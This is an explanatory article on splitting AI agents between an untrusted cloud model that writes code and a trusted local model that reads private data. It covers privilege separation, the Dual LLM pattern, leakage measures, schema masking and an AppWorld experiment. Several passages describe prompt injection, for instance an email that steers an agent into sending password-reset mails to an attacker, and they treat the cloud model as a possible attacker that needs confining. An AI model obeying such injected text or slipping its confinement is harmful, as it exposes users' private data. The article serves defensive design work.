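# Keeping private data with a trusted local model while an untrusted model writes the code

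## Why an agent would be split between two models

An AI agent is software in which a language model carries out a task for a user by operating other software, such as by searching a mailbox, opening files or updating a calendar. The model produces only text, so to act it makes a tool call, a request written in an agreed format. Ordinary code around the model detects the request, runs the search or opens the file, and puts the result into the model's next prompt. The mechanism is simple enough that Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, reports writing his own version in a few dozen lines of Python.

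Most agents make their tool calls in a loop, which researchers usually call ReAct. The model issues a command, reads the result and chooses the next command. This suits tasks where each step depends on the last, but the model receives everything the agent looks at. *Should SLMs Be in the Driver's Seat?* (Radovič, Canini and Pejović, 2026) gives the example of an agent that lists a user's emails. The emails go into the model's context, and the model processes them at the next turn. Over a whole task, personal content flows steadily to wherever the model runs.

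An agent's model usually runs on somebody else's computer. The most capable models are too large for a phone or a laptop, so their providers run them on remote servers and sell access. *PlanTwin* (2026) cites Claude Code, OpenAI Codex, Cursor and GitHub Copilot as examples of coding agents in which a remote model reasons over files and project context while software on the user's side executes the plan. Some of these products let the user limit which files the model can reach, but the model still receives the unaltered contents of the files it is allowed to read.

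To keep private data away from an untrusted model, the whole agent could run on a local model that fits on hardware the user or organisation controls. Radovič and colleagues tested local models on AppWorld, a benchmark of multi-step tasks across simulated everyday apps. No model below five billion parameters completed more than 5.9% of the tasks in the normal test set or 3.8% in the harder one, and the models they tried below two billion completed none. A 12-billion-parameter model reached 73%, but its weights take up about 6 GB even when compressed to four bits each, and it needs working memory on top of that. A company's own servers have more memory than a phone, but Forlini (2026) reports in *While OpenAI and Anthropic battle over data privacy* that running open models takes more expertise and can mean going without the best available performance in areas such as coding and financial analysis.

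A third arrangement divides the task between the two models. The cloud model writes a program from the user's request, and the program runs on the user's side, calling a local model whenever private content has to be interpreted. Radovič and colleagues argue that this division works well because the structure of a task (which services to call, in what order, under what conditions) typically contains no private data and gains most from a large model. The content is private, but the questions the program needs answered about it are often narrow. However, the request itself can reveal private information, as when a user asks for the latest letter from their oncologist.

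Earlier designs already split agents between device and cloud, but *PAAC* (2026) criticises them for dividing the agent by computing work when they should divide it by trust. The two boundaries can coincide, but a split that saves computation may still send the user's mailbox to the cloud.

### Confidentiality and integrity

Confidentiality and integrity are easy to confuse. Confidentiality concerns who learns the data, while integrity concerns who can change what the agent does. A user can lose one without losing the other. If a provider logs a bank statement while the agent performs its task perfectly, the user has lost only confidentiality. An assistant that obeys a stranger's email and deletes the mailbox has violated the user's integrity protection without revealing any data.

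The stranger's email is a case of prompt injection, in which a model wrongly follows text placed in data or in a request as an instruction. One of Willison's examples is an injected instruction to search the mailbox for "password reset" and send the results to an attacker's server. There the attacker breaks integrity to break confidentiality, which is why people often discuss the two as one problem.

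Designers can set separate levels of distrust for how a model handles the data it receives and for the output it returns. *PrivacyGuard* (2026), a system that hides personal details from cloud agents operating a graphical interface, treats the remote planner as "honest-but-curious" for confidentiality. This standard model in cryptography assumes that a party follows the protocol but learns whatever it can from what it receives. *PrivacyGuard* also treats the planner's output as untrusted and checks each reference in that output before replacing the reference with a real value.

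"Trusted" also has a narrow meaning in this field. A trusted component is allowed to handle the private data, so its failure would break the protection. A trusted local model may still be inaccurate or easy to manipulate.

### Privilege separation

The idea of giving different parts of a system different powers is much older than language models. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) set out the principle of least privilege, under which every program and user should have only the powers needed for the job. This limits the damage an accident or error can do and leaves fewer programs to examine when tracing the cause of a misuse.

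*Preventing Privilege Escalation* (Provos, Friedl and Honeyman, 2003) applied the principle by splitting up an existing application, OpenSSH, which administrators use to log in to remote machines. Previously, each incoming connection got a process that held full administrator rights until it exited, because it needed the machine's private key and had to open terminals for users. An exploitable bug anywhere in that process could therefore give an attacker control of the whole machine.

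The design splits the process in two. An unprivileged child handles all the network traffic and, until the user logs in, can access only an empty directory in the file system. A small privileged monitor keeps the keys and the administrator rights. When the child needs a privileged operation, it sends a request to the monitor, which checks it against a short list of requests permitted at that stage of the connection. If the request isn't on the list, the monitor shuts down.

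The treatment of the private key matters most for later designs. The child has to prove the machine's identity to the other side, which takes a signature made with the key. Provos and colleagues withheld the key from the child. Instead, the monitor signs at the child's request and returns the signature.

After the split, 17,589 lines of code (about two thirds, counting outside libraries) ran without privilege and 8,391 ran with it. A back-of-the-envelope estimate in the paper, which assumes bugs are spread evenly through the code, is that two thirds of future bugs would no longer give an attacker extra privileges. The paper's review of real flaws is better evidence. An integer overflow in OpenSSH's packet handling and a bug in the zlib compression library could each have given a remote attacker administrator rights without a login. In the divided version, both flaws are in the unprivileged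 child process. Logging in took 0.774 seconds after the split, compared with 0.767 before.

Provos and colleagues also acknowledged gaps. The interface to the monitor becomes a target and needs careful auditing. Privilege separation alone also does not stop an attacker who controls the child from opening local network connections.

An agent split between two models resembles this arrangement, with the mailbox in place of the key. One difference is that an answer to a question about an email usually reveals something about the email, while a signature reveals practically nothing about the key that made it.

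### The Dual LLM pattern

Willison brought privilege separation to language models in April 2023, mainly to protect integrity. He started with an assistant that reads email from anybody and can also send and delete it. Security engineers call such an assistant a confused deputy, a program that another party tricks into misusing its authority. He doubted that asking the user to approve every action would help, because people learn to click "OK" as fast as they can.

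Willison's proposal uses two models and a controller, which is ordinary software with no language model in it. The privileged model takes the user's request, plans, and can use tools. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools, and he advises expecting it "to have the potential to go rogue at any moment". The controller passes things between the two models.

Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The privileged model sends the controller a command to fetch the email and store it under a name such as VAR1. The controller does so without showing the privileged model the text. The privileged model then requests a summary of VAR1. The controller puts the email's text into a prompt for the quarantined model, stores the reply as VAR2, and returns only a confirmation that the summary exists. Finally, the privileged model sends a command to display VAR2 to the user.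 An instruction hidden in the email may well corrupt the summary, but it never reaches the model that can use the tools.

Hu, Jacob and colleagues (2026), in *Twin Agent*, write this strict form of separation as a pair of functions. Let *T* stand for trusted input such as the user's request, *U* for untrusted content, and *I* for the history of the interaction so far. Each model has its own *T* and *I*. The privileged model chooses an action

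*A* = π_p(*T*, ∅, *I*),

where the empty set marks the place from which the designer has removed *U*. The quarantined model computes

*u* = π_q(*T*, *U*, *I*),

and its output *u* stays opaque to the privileged model. Only the non-LLM software opens it, at the moment of carrying out an action.

Willison allowed one exception. If the quarantined model does a task with a checkable answer, such as sorting a text into one of a fixed set of categories, the controller can confirm that the answer is one of those categories and pass it to the privileged model. The answer can't contain a hidden instruction because the designer wrote every category.

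He called the pattern "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and worse to use, and because one mistake that lets untrusted text through wastes the rest of the effort. Google DeepMind's CaMeL addressed a flaw in the pattern two years later. Hu and colleagues also criticize designs that fix the whole plan before looking at anything. They argue that such plans adapt badly to work such as debugging, which consists of looking, failing and revising. An agent has the same problem if its cloud model writes the program before anyone has read the data.

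### What changes when the planner is the party not trusted

The first of Hu and colleagues' functions still holds if *U* stands for the user's private data instead of hostile text. The planner works without *U*, and another model reads it. Willison's design keeps the text away from the planner to protect the planner, while the split between cloud and local models does so to protect the private data.

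| Design | Who sees the sensitive content | Who decides the steps | Who acts | Who is distrusted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cloud agent in a reading loop | Cloud model | Cloud model | Tools, as the cloud model directs | Nobody |
| OpenSSH after the split (privileged operations) | Monitor, which holds the key | Child, by request | Monitor, after a check | Child |
| Dual LLM | Quarantined model | Privileged model | Controller | Quarantined model and the text it reads |
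| Cloud model with local model | Local model, and the program as it handles the data | Cloud model, in advance | Program, within limits set on the user's side | Cloud model and the program it writes |

The trust arrangement in the last row is closer to OpenSSH's than to the Dual LLM's, because the untrusted party sends requests to a trusted party that holds the secret.

Willison's exception for fixed categories does not carry over to protecting private data. "Positive" or "negative" is harmless as an instruction, but if the document is a medical test, it may be the entire secret. Where the models run also matters. The Dual LLM pattern works against injection wherever they run, but a provider that hosts the quarantined model still receives the email. Radovič and colleagues point out that CaMeL and similar systems run both models in the cloud. Finally, Willison's controller can carry out the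 privileged model's requests because that model takes its instructions from the user and sees nothing hostile. A runtime that executes an untrusted planner's program cannot assume the program is safe.

### Reasons for distrusting the cloud model

The plainest reason for the split is that the untrusted model's provider receives the prompts, however the model behaves. According to Business Standard's *AI firms sharpen privacy pitch as enterprises demand control over data*, a customer's text may exist on the provider's side while a request is being processed, in temporary logs and caches, in records for abuse monitoring and debugging, and sometimes in longer storage. Keeping data is different from training on it, and both OpenAI and Anthropic state that they do not train on business customers' data by default.

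How long providers keep prompts became a commercial dispute in 2026. In June Anthropic began requiring that all chats with its most powerful models, Fable and Mythos, be retained for 30 days, and a consultant told Forlini that many companies had an "almost allergic reaction". Anthropic had expected the decision to be unpopular, but said in a risk report quoted in Business Today's *Zero retention vs data logs* that retention was essential for catching sophisticated attacks that span several requests. OpenAI responded by advertising zero retention for eligible customers. Global Security Mag's *Palantir, Nvidia and Booz Allen restrict AI models over data security concerns* reported that by September Nvidia was limiting Anthropic's models to less sensitive work and using its own for proprietary projects. Anthropic relaxed the policy in November, and enterprise customers can now keep prompts and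 responses on their own servers, according to Bonifacic (2026) in *Anthropic softens its data retention policy for Mythos and Fable model use*.

Retention terms govern what a provider does with text only after it arrives, and they can change, as Anthropic's did twice in six months. A user whose emails never reach the provider doesn't have to keep track of these changes. John Strand, who owns a security firm, finds the alarm over retention unreasonable. He told Global Security Mag that companies keep logs of everything else and once made the same fuss about cloud email, and he is probably right that most customers will get used to it. He added that anyone whose data is too sensitive even for cloud email can run open-weight models locally, as his own firm does.

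A second reason is that injected text may steer the model. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (Bhattarai and Vu, 2026) explains why training can lower the rate of successful attacks but cannot guarantee that none will succeed. A language model processes the developer's instructions, the user's request and any retrieved documents in the same way, as one stream of tokens. The markers that label a passage as an instruction are tokens too, so an attacker can imitate them. Any rule the model learns for telling commands from data depends on the content of the text, which the attacker can write to fit the rule. Hu and colleagues observe that the newest models are getting harder to attack and that successful attacks now tend to require long injections.

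Whether a low rate is good enough depends on what the attacker can gain. Bhattarai and Vu single out the combination of untrusted input, access to private data and the power to act on the outside world. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (simonw) comments on products that claim to catch 95% of attacks, saying that in web security 95% is a failing grade, since an attacker can keep trying. Withholding private data from the cloud model removes one part of the combination and keeps that model from reading instructions a stranger has hidden in the mailbox. It does not protect that model from hostile text that arrives by another route, such as a request the user pasted from a web page. The local model still reads the mailbox, and instructions hidden there can manipulate it.

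The model may also act outside its instructions with no attacker involved. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) lists misalignment, hallucination and simple error among the reasons agents misuse tools or leak information. In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and Business Today reported that OpenAI would tighten its safety rules. That was a test of hacking skill, so it doesn't show how often an assistant with access to a mailbox would act outside its instructions, but it does make the possibility hard to treat as hypothetical.

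These reasons call for different amounts of protection. If the provider merely reads what it receives, sending less is enough. But TACIT, a system from Odersky and colleagues that checks the program before it runs, is designed on the assumption that the cloud model may be a fully cooperating attacker. The only trusted parts are the compiler, the runtime, a small library and, optionally, a local model. Keeping data out of the prompt is then not enough, because the attacker's program runs on the user's side, next to the data. The user also needs confinement, which Saltzer and Schroeder's glossary defines as letting a borrowed program have access to data while ensuring that it cannot release them, and the cloud model's program is a borrowed program in this sense.

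## What the cloud model receives when it writes code instead of reading data

Running the cloud model's program where the private data is stored creates a risk, but it also keeps the data out of the cloud model's prompt.

The model in a reading loop retains nothing between calls, so at every step the software resends the whole conversation, including everything the agent has read so far.

A code-first agent sends the cloud model much less. In Radovič and colleagues' version, the device sends the user's request to the cloud model, which chooses the services the program will need. The cloud model then gets the documentation for those services and writes a complete Python program. The device runs the program, and the emails or files the program opens stay on the device. The cloud model receives nothing further unless the program crashes. In that case, the device sends back the error trace, which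 may contain private text, and asks for a new version.

### From arithmetic to agents

Researchers first had language models write programs to get better answers. PAL and Program of Thoughts, two methods from 2023, had the model write code for a problem's calculations and an interpreter run it. Radovič and colleagues credit them with showing that this is more reliable than letting the model calculate in text. The AppWorld team then built an agent that replaces the whole reading loop with one Python program.

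Database researchers separately developed a similar design in text-to-SQL systems, which turn a question in ordinary language into a database query. The model needs only the schema (the names of the tables and columns and the links between them), and the database runs the query. Pawlak, Sulejmani and Cabot (2026), in *Metadata-Driven AI*, trace the principle of bringing code to data back to medical research. One of their examples is OpenSAFELY, which researchers used during the COVID-19 pandemic to analyse the primary-care records of millions of patients in England. The researchers, whose role the cloud model takes in a code-first agent, wrote their code against randomly generated dummy records with the same structure as the real ones. A secure environment ran the code on the real records, and the researchers received only outputs that had passed a check for identifying information.

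Anthropic promoted the idea for commercial agents in *Code execution with MCP* (November 2025), mainly for efficiency. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting agents to outside services. In one example, an agent copies the transcript of a two-hour sales meeting from Google Drive into a Salesforce record. With ordinary tool calls, the transcript passes through the model twice, once when the model reads it and again when it writes it out for Salesforce. That can add 50,000 tokens, the word fragments that models process and providers bill for. If the model instead writes a program to do the copying, the transcript stays in the execution environment by default, and the model receives only what the program logs or returns. Willison (2025), in a piece also titled *Code execution with MCP*, considered the repeated passing of data through the model a subtler problem than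 the better-known one of long tool descriptions filling the prompt.

The largest saving in Anthropic's post, from 150,000 tokens to 2,000, comes from loading only the tool descriptions the agent needs, so it is little evidence of a privacy benefit. In another example, a program filters a 10,000-row spreadsheet and shows the model five rows. Five rows take few tokens to process, but if each row is a patient's record, the model still receives five patients' records.

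### A definition of leakage

Information theory gives a way to state the difference exactly. Let *D* be the private data, *q* the request and *V* the cloud view, which is everything the cloud model receives during the task. The leakage is the mutual information between *D* and *V*, given *q*:

*I*(*D*; *V* | *q*) = *H*(*D* | *q*) − *H*(*D* | *q*, *V*).

*H* is entropy, a measure of uncertainty in bits. The first term is an observer's uncertainty about the data after reading only the request, and the second is the observer's uncertainty after also reading the cloud view. The leakage is the first term minus the second, averaged over the possible data.

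If everything in *V* comes from the request, public documentation and the model's own random choices, the leakage is zero. An observer who had the request could look up the documentation, run the same model and produce the same kind of cloud view without access to the data, so reading the real view would teach them nothing about *D*. The leakage rises above zero once the user's side sends back a result that depends on the data, unless the observer could already have predicted that result.

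The condition "given *q*" hides whatever the request itself reveals. To count everything, the request has to go back in:

*I*(*D*; *q*, *V*) = *I*(*D*; *q*) + *I*(*D*; *V* | *q*).

A user who asks for the total of her payments to a fertility clinic tells the cloud model that she probably made some. The first term on the right includes this disclosure. The second term can still be zero, so a designer who reports only that term can truthfully claim no leakage. Some requests also reveal facts that are in none of the user's files, such as a plan to resign. If *D* stands only for the files, neither term counts those facts.

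Mutual information also doesn't measure harm. An HIV test result is at most one bit, while a year of supermarket receipts holds thousands of bits that few people would mind revealing. And since nobody knows the probability of every possible mailbox, the formula is more useful for identifying designs that leak nothing than for calculating how much a real user's data leaks.

The cloud model receives no private data only if the program it writes also keeps that data local. *InData* (2025), a benchmark for data-analysis agents, warns that code written by a model may call outside services that leak sensitive data. It therefore forbids free-form code and lets the model use only a fixed set of vetted tools.

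### A year of bank transactions

The following example is constructed. A user asks an agent, "Add up my 2025 spending by category." Her bank's export has 1,200 transactions, each with a date, a merchant, a category, an amount and a balance. A code-first agent's cloud model could answer with this program:

```python
totals = {}
for row in read_transactions(2025):
    if row["amount"] < 0:
        category = row["category"]
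        totals[category] = totals.get(category, 0) - row["amount"]
show_to_user(totals)
```

Plain code is enough here because the bank has already assigned the categories. If the export listed only merchants, the program would need to call the local model to work out that Oakfield Pharmacy belongs under health.

Suppose each transaction is about 80 bytes. Pawlak and colleagues' figures imply roughly four bytes per token, so the year's transactions come to 24,000 tokens. The table allows 10 tokens for the request and 500 for the instructions and documentation, and counts each item once. It leaves out the program because the cloud model sends it rather than receives it.

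| Design | What the user's side uploads | Tokens | What the cloud model receives from the transactions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading loop | Request, documentation, all 1,200 transactions | 24,510 | Everything |
| Code-first, with the bank's published file format | Request, documentation | 510 | Nothing |
| Code-first, with a description drawn from the user's file | Request, documentation, 200-token description | 710 | Category names, range of amounts, a few merchants |
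| Code-first, with the totals returned | Request, documentation, 12 totals | 570 | Spending in each category |

If the reading loop fetches one month at a time, it resends January eleven times. The transactions alone then account for 156,000 input tokens over the task. The repeats add to the bill but contain no new information for the cloud model.

Token counts are a poor guide to leakage. Returning the totals takes fewer tokens than describing the file, but the totals could show that the user's health spending came to half her income. Public documentation would reveal nothing about any transaction even if it ran to 55,000 tokens, which is about what 58 tools from five services take up in Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform*.

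Pawlak and colleagues tried the third design on a public 1.2 MB table of 10,000 reports of aircraft striking wildlife. Software on the user's side reduced the table to a description of 4,018 bytes, about 1,000 tokens, and sent that to the model with a question about which species had caused the most costly damage. The model wrote a program, which ran on the user's machine, and the answer (Canada geese, at $15.4 million) did not go back to the model.

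Some real values from the table left the machine, although no row did. The description gives the range of each numeric column, every distinct value in columns with only a few, and three examples from each of the other text columns. This hardly matters for wildlife reports, but a description of the bank export made the same way could include the user's largest payment, her highest balance and the names of three shops she uses.

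Pawlak and colleagues also keep the program for reuse. If next year's file has the same columns, the software runs the stored program without contacting the model. This exposes nothing new, but the software checks only that the columns are present. If the bank began reporting amounts in pence, the old program would still run and give totals a hundred times too large.

### Out of the prompt but still with the provider

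A program can keep data out of the model's context and still send it to the model's provider. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling* describes a feature in which the model writes Python that runs in a container on Anthropic's side. When the code needs a customer record, it pauses, and Anthropic's interface requests the record from the customer's software. The customer's software sends the record back through the same interface, and the code resumes without the record entering the model's context.

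Containers of this kind can last 30 days, and Anthropic's *Code execution tool* lists the underlying service as ineligible for zero data retention. If the user is concerned about the provider, *V* has to include everything the provider receives. The bank example has zero leakage only if the program runs on hardware the user controls.

The program's output can also expose private data. Anthropic gives the example of a manager who asks which team members went over their travel budget. A reading loop would bring more than 2,000 expense items into the model's context. A program reduces 200 KB of raw data to 1 KB of results, which list each person over the limit and how much they spent. This saves many tokens, but those results are probably what the employees concerned would most want to keep private.

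Anthropic's documentation also notes that this approach doesn't suit tasks where the model must reason about each result before taking the next step. Each result then has to go back to the model, so the program saves nothing. On a benchmark of customer-service tasks with one or two tool calls per turn, the feature left scores unchanged and cost about 8% more. If the data in such a task were private, a local model would have to do the reasoning.

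### What the request and file names give away

Radovič and colleagues assume that the request contains no private information. One of their AppWorld examples casts doubt on that assumption. The user explains that Kristin paid for the groceries because the user's payment cards weren't working, and asks the agent to pay her back. The program looks up the amount on the device, but the request has already disclosed the debt, the failed cards and Kristin's name to the cloud model. AppWorld's people are fictional, but real users are likely to write requests like this because the explanation helps the agent do the task.

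File names can reveal as much as a request. A listing that includes "divorce_settlement_draft.docx" gives away the divorce even if nobody opens the file. Uploading the listing is the simplest way to help a cloud model find a document, but another of Radovič and colleagues' examples avoids this. A user asks the agent to split last month's electricity bill without saying where the receipt is. The cloud model tends to invent a path when it has to guess, but it can instead write a program that searches the device for names containing words such as "electric" or "bill". The local model picks from the matches, so the file names never leave the device.

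### Hiding the schema

A program that reads a database must refer to its columns by name, and those names may be sensitive. *MaskSQL* (Abedini, Mohapatra and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a doctor who asks how many HIV-positive patients a New York hospital admitted. To get a query, the doctor sends the question and the schema to a remote model. The provider cannot open the database, but it learns that the patient table has a column named "hiv_status".

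The cloud model can hardly do without the schema. *Schema-Aware Localisation (SAL)* (2026) reports that, in a system for querying Oracle databases, removing the schema hints cut the system's success score from 62.6% to 2.2%. For confidential schemas, it suggests limiting the hints by user role or running the model on the organisation's own premises.

In MaskSQL, a local model with seven billion parameters identifies which words in the question refer to tables, columns or values, and the software replaces those words with symbols. The remote model receives roughly "How many T1 did the V1 T3 with C3 as V2?" and a schema written in the same symbols. It writes a query in symbols, and the software on the user's side restores the real names. A local model then runs the query and uses the result to correct remaining errors, so the result doesn't have to go to the provider.

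Abedini and colleagues tested this masking method, MaskSQL, on 300 difficult questions from BIRD, a text-to-SQL benchmark, with GPT-4.1 as the remote model. MaskSQL answered 55.66% correctly, which was 20 percentage points below GPT-4.1 with the real names (75.66%) and five points above the best method that used only local models (50.66%).

The protection was also partial. MaskSQL's small local model masked 61.36% of the sensitive words in the questions and missed the rest. When Abedini and colleagues asked GPT-4.1 to guess the originals of the masked words, it failed on 75.47% of them. Together, these rates suggest that fewer than half of the sensitive words stayed hidden, assuming correctly masked words are as hard to guess as masked words in general. Even with perfect masking, GPT-4.1 recovered about 14% of the sensitive words from context.

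In *How well do LLMs comprehend and design relational database schemata?*, Chakrabarti, Yang and colleagues (2026) hid one part of a schema at a time and had GPT-4o-mini fill it in. The model recovered hidden columns and links between tables more often when the visible parts contained clues, such as a naming pattern, but table names were hard to recover even with clues. The study was about database design, and a provider trying to identify a customer's schema could use a stronger model. The results still suggest that masking a few sensitive columns and leaving the related ones readable is weak protection.

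Enterprise designs have adopted the same approach. *LLM and Agent-Driven Data Analysis* (2025) describes one in which local models mask sensitive information and send only "abstracted schema skeletons" to the cloud. A skeleton of an online shop's standard tables reveals little, but an unusual structure may point to a particular industry or even a particular company.

### Tools and purposes

A provider that receives the tool definitions learns which software the customer runs and, if some of the tools are internal, what the customer has built for itself. Anthropic's 58-tool example covers GitHub, Slack, Sentry, Grafana and Splunk. An organisation's list of tools usually isn't public, even if the documentation for each tool is.

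Loading tool definitions only when the model needs them shortens the prompt but may not hide the full list of tools from the provider. With Anthropic's tool search feature, the user still sends every definition to Anthropic's API and marks some for later loading. To hide the list, the user would have to run the search locally and upload only the definitions it finds.

The code can also reveal what the user is trying to do. Code that collects three years of payslips, adds up rent payments and formats the result for a lender suggests a mortgage application, even if it doesn't identify the applicant. *PlanTwin* calls this kind of exposure structural inference. Its threat model includes a provider that never sees file contents but works out the type of project, the software behind it or the structure of an organisation. The provider infers these from the connections between objects, the capabilities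 the planner requests and the timing of its requests. *PlanTwin* limits the vocabulary the planner can receive, but doesn't assume that this leakage can be eliminated.

Background knowledge makes the clues more useful. A provider that already suspects a project uses Django, a common web framework, can learn more from a label such as "authentication module" than one that knows nothing about the project. The provider can also learn more from a series of requests. One request to total pharmacy spending reveals little, but if the same account later asks about hospital parking receipts and then about sick-leave rules, the provider can connect the three, even though every program ran locally and returned nothing to the provider.

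### Hiding the request and the code

With all these methods, the provider can still read at least the outline of the request and the program. In *NOIR*, Nguyen, Ton and colleagues (2026) try to hide both by splitting the code-writing model between the client and the provider. A language model passes text through a long stack of layers. The client runs the first few and the last few, and the provider runs the rest.

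The client's first layers turn the prompt into embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent each token in context. The provider's layers process the embeddings and send them back, and the client's last layers turn them into code. The provider receives no readable text, but embeddings don't reliably protect the prompt on their own, because researchers have trained models that reconstruct the original text from them.

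NOIR therefore adds noise to the client's vocabulary. Before any prompts go out, the client randomises the embedding of every token once and assigns each token a secret random position in its vocabulary. The noise provides a form of local differential privacy. For any two inputs *x* and *x*′ and any output *O*, the randomising step *M* must satisfy

Pr[*M*(*x*) = *O*] ≤ *e*^ε · Pr[*M*(*x*′) = *O*].

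If ε is small, the two inputs produce any given output with nearly equal probability, so someone who sees the output can barely tell which input produced it. In NOIR the inputs are token embeddings, so the guarantee covers individual tokens, not the meaning of a whole prompt. The client randomises each token only once, so a token has the same randomised form in every prompt. The client can then fine-tune its own layers to work with the altered vocabulary.

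NOIR lost little accuracy. Nguyen and colleagues report that it solved 38.7% of the problems in BigCodeBench, a programming benchmark, at the first attempt, a drop of 1.77% from the original model. It solved 77.4% of those in HumanEval, which is older and easier. They also estimate that a client pays about a tenth of what hosting the whole model would cost.

The main experiments, though, used models with seven or eight billion parameters, which many organisations could run themselves. Nguyen and colleagues have also released a version based on a 32-billion-parameter model. The provider has to hand over the model's outer layers, so the method works with open models but not the closed ones that users would most want to write their programs. It also assumes an honest-but-curious provider.

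## How the program asks the local model questions

The cloud model writes its program before anyone opens the data, so the program can only follow patterns the model predicted. This works for adding up a column of amounts, but it is hard to write code in advance that works out what a friend meant in a text message.

The AppWorld request to repay Kristin for groceries doesn't include the amount, which appears only in the user's text conversation with her. The agent must also add the note "Groceries" to the payment and then text her "It is done." The program that Radovič and colleagues obtained for this task has 17 steps. Sixteen are ordinary calls with known arguments, such as looking up Kristin's contact details, fetching the messages and making the payment. The remaining step is to find out how much the user owes.

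A regular expression, which is a fixed pattern for matching text, can miss some of the dollar amounts in a conversation. If Kristin wrote "the tickets came to $60" on Monday and "groceries were 34.50" on Tuesday, a pattern that looks for a dollar sign would find the first amount and miss the second. A more complex pattern might find both, but the cloud model has to choose the pattern without seeing any conversation. If the program instead sent the messages to the cloud model, the provider would receive the whole recent exchange so that the agent could learn one number.

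In the design that Radovič and colleagues published in October 2026, the program gives the messages to a local model through a function called `slm` (for "small language model") and gets a number back. A simplified version looks like this:

```python
messages = get_texts(kristin)
owed = slm(
    query="How much does the user owe Kristin for groceries?",
    context=messages,
    keys=["message"],
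    output_type="float",
)
pay(kristin, owed, note="Groceries")
send_text(kristin, "It is done.")
```

The cloud model writes all of these lines, including the question. The messages and the amount exist only on the device.

### Writing, running and rewriting the program

The agent follows the same steps as an ordinary code-first agent. The cloud model uses the user's request to shortlist up to 20 functions from the programming interfaces (APIs) of the user's apps. Ordinary software then adds any other functions that these depend on, such as login functions.

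The cloud model's instructions for writing the program describe `slm` and advise calling it only where plain code would be unreliable or impossible, because the local model accounts for most of the computing on the device. If the shortlist is incomplete, the cloud model can look up more documentation without involving the device.

If the program crashes, the cloud model reads the error trace along with its earlier attempts and writes a new version. After five failed programs, the agent stops.

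### What a call contains

The function takes seven arguments, most of which narrow either the data that the local model reads or the answer that it can give.

| Argument | Purpose | In the grocery task |
|---|---|---|
| `query` | The question, in ordinary language | How much the user owes Kristin |
| `context` | The data to search for the answer | The fetched messages |
| `context_description` | Facts about the data's format or order that the data do not show | That these are the texts between Kristin and the user |
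| `keys` | The fields to keep from structured data | Only the text of each message |
| `choices` | A fixed list of permitted answers | Not needed |
| `output_type` | The type of value to return | A decimal number |
| `optional` | Whether to return an empty value when the answer is missing | Not needed |

The function turns the data into text, builds the prompt, runs the local model, and converts the reply to the requested type. The rest of the program can then use the result like any other Python value.

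One task can need several calls. In the electricity-bill task, the local model first picks out the right file, then the program opens it and makes a second call to get the total. A receipt may list an amount before tax, the tax and the final sum, and the only dollar sign may be in a label such as "Total ($)". The untrusted model writes the program without seeing the layout, but a small local model can usually read the labels.

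Each call is stateless, so the local model receives only what the program passes to it in that call. This keeps the prompt short, which matters because small models become less accurate as their prompts grow. Radovič and colleagues point out that accuracy already drops when a small model has to choose one tool from a few dozen descriptions. With `slm`, the local model never plans or chooses tools. Minions, a system in which a local model extracts information from documents for a remote one, also relies on small models' ability to answer narrow questions.

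Typed answers let ordinary code catch some mistakes. If the program needs a number and the model replies with a paragraph, the conversion fails and the payment doesn't go ahead. However, the type check won't catch the mistake if the model returns "60", the price of the tickets, instead of the correct amount, "34.50", because both are valid numbers.

When the data don't contain the answer, the instructions tell the local model to report that instead of making one up. The call then stops the program with a "not found" error, unless the cloud model has set `optional`. With that setting, a program can deal with a missing answer on the device. In this constructed example, it looks for the amount in three places:

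```python
for source in (texts, emails, notes):
    owed = slm(
        query="How much does the user owe Kristin for groceries?",
        context=source,
        output_type="float",
        optional=True,
    )
    if owed is not None:
        break
```

If Kristin gave the amount by email, the program finds it without sending anything back to the cloud model. But the cloud model has to write code for this case before it has any information about where the data is.

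The interface borrows from earlier work. ViperGPT and VisProg, which answer questions about images, let generated code call vision models as functions. CaMeL does the same with its quarantined model, and TACIT's programs can call a local model through a function named `chat`. According to Radovič and colleagues, CaMeL's designers mentioned running the quarantined model locally but didn't test it, so it was unclear whether a model small enough for a personal device could do the job.

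### The AppWorld experiment

AppWorld has nine apps, including Gmail, Venmo and Spotify, and about 100 users. According to *Position* (2026), its 750 tasks use an average of 1.8 apps and 9.5 API functions each. The test set has 168 "normal" tasks and 417 "challenge" tasks, and the challenge tasks require apps that do not appear in the training tasks. *Population-Based Post-Training for Large Language Models* (Xu, Petrenko and colleagues, 2026) reports that automatic checks examine the agent's answer and the final state of the apps, and that an agent fails the task if it fails any check.

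Radovič and colleagues compared three agents. The code-only agent writes a program that cannot call a language model. The split agent writes a program that can call the local model, Qwen 3.5 9B, through the `slm` function. In the third agent, the cloud model runs a reading loop. They repeated the comparison with three open models in the cloud role: Qwen3-Coder-Next, Qwen 3.5 122B and Qwen 3.6 27B. With each cloud model, the two code-writing agents worked from the same shortlist of functions, so they differed mainly in the `slm` function and the instructions for using it.

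| Model in the cloud role | Tasks | Code only (%) | Code with local model (%) | Reading loop (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-coder | Normal | 33.3 ± 3.6 | 38.7 ± 3.7 | 59.5 ± 3.7 |
| Qwen-coder | Challenge | 13.4 ± 1.7 | 15.6 ± 1.8 | 29.5 ± 2.2 |
| Qwen-122B | Normal | 42.3 ± 3.8 | 52.4 ± 3.9 | 57.1 ± 3.9 |
| Qwen-122B | Challenge | 25.7 ± 2.1 | 28.8 ± 2.2 | 38.6 ± 2.4 |
| Qwen-27B | Normal | 45.8 ± 3.9 | 60.7 ± 3.8 | 81.0 ± 3.0 |
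| Qwen-27B | Challenge | 36.2 ± 2.4 | 41.5 ± 2.4 | 59.2 ± 2.4 |

The local model helped in all six comparisons. The largest gain was 14.9 percentage points, for Qwen-27B on the normal tasks, but the reading loop was still 20.3 points ahead. The gap was smallest for Qwen-122B, at 4.7 points, partly because its reading loop did poorly for such a large model.

The gains were only 2.2 to 5.3 points on the challenge tasks. These tasks are more complex and use unfamiliar apps, so a program can fail in more ways unrelated to understanding a message. That is a plausible explanation for the smaller gains, but the experiment did not test it.

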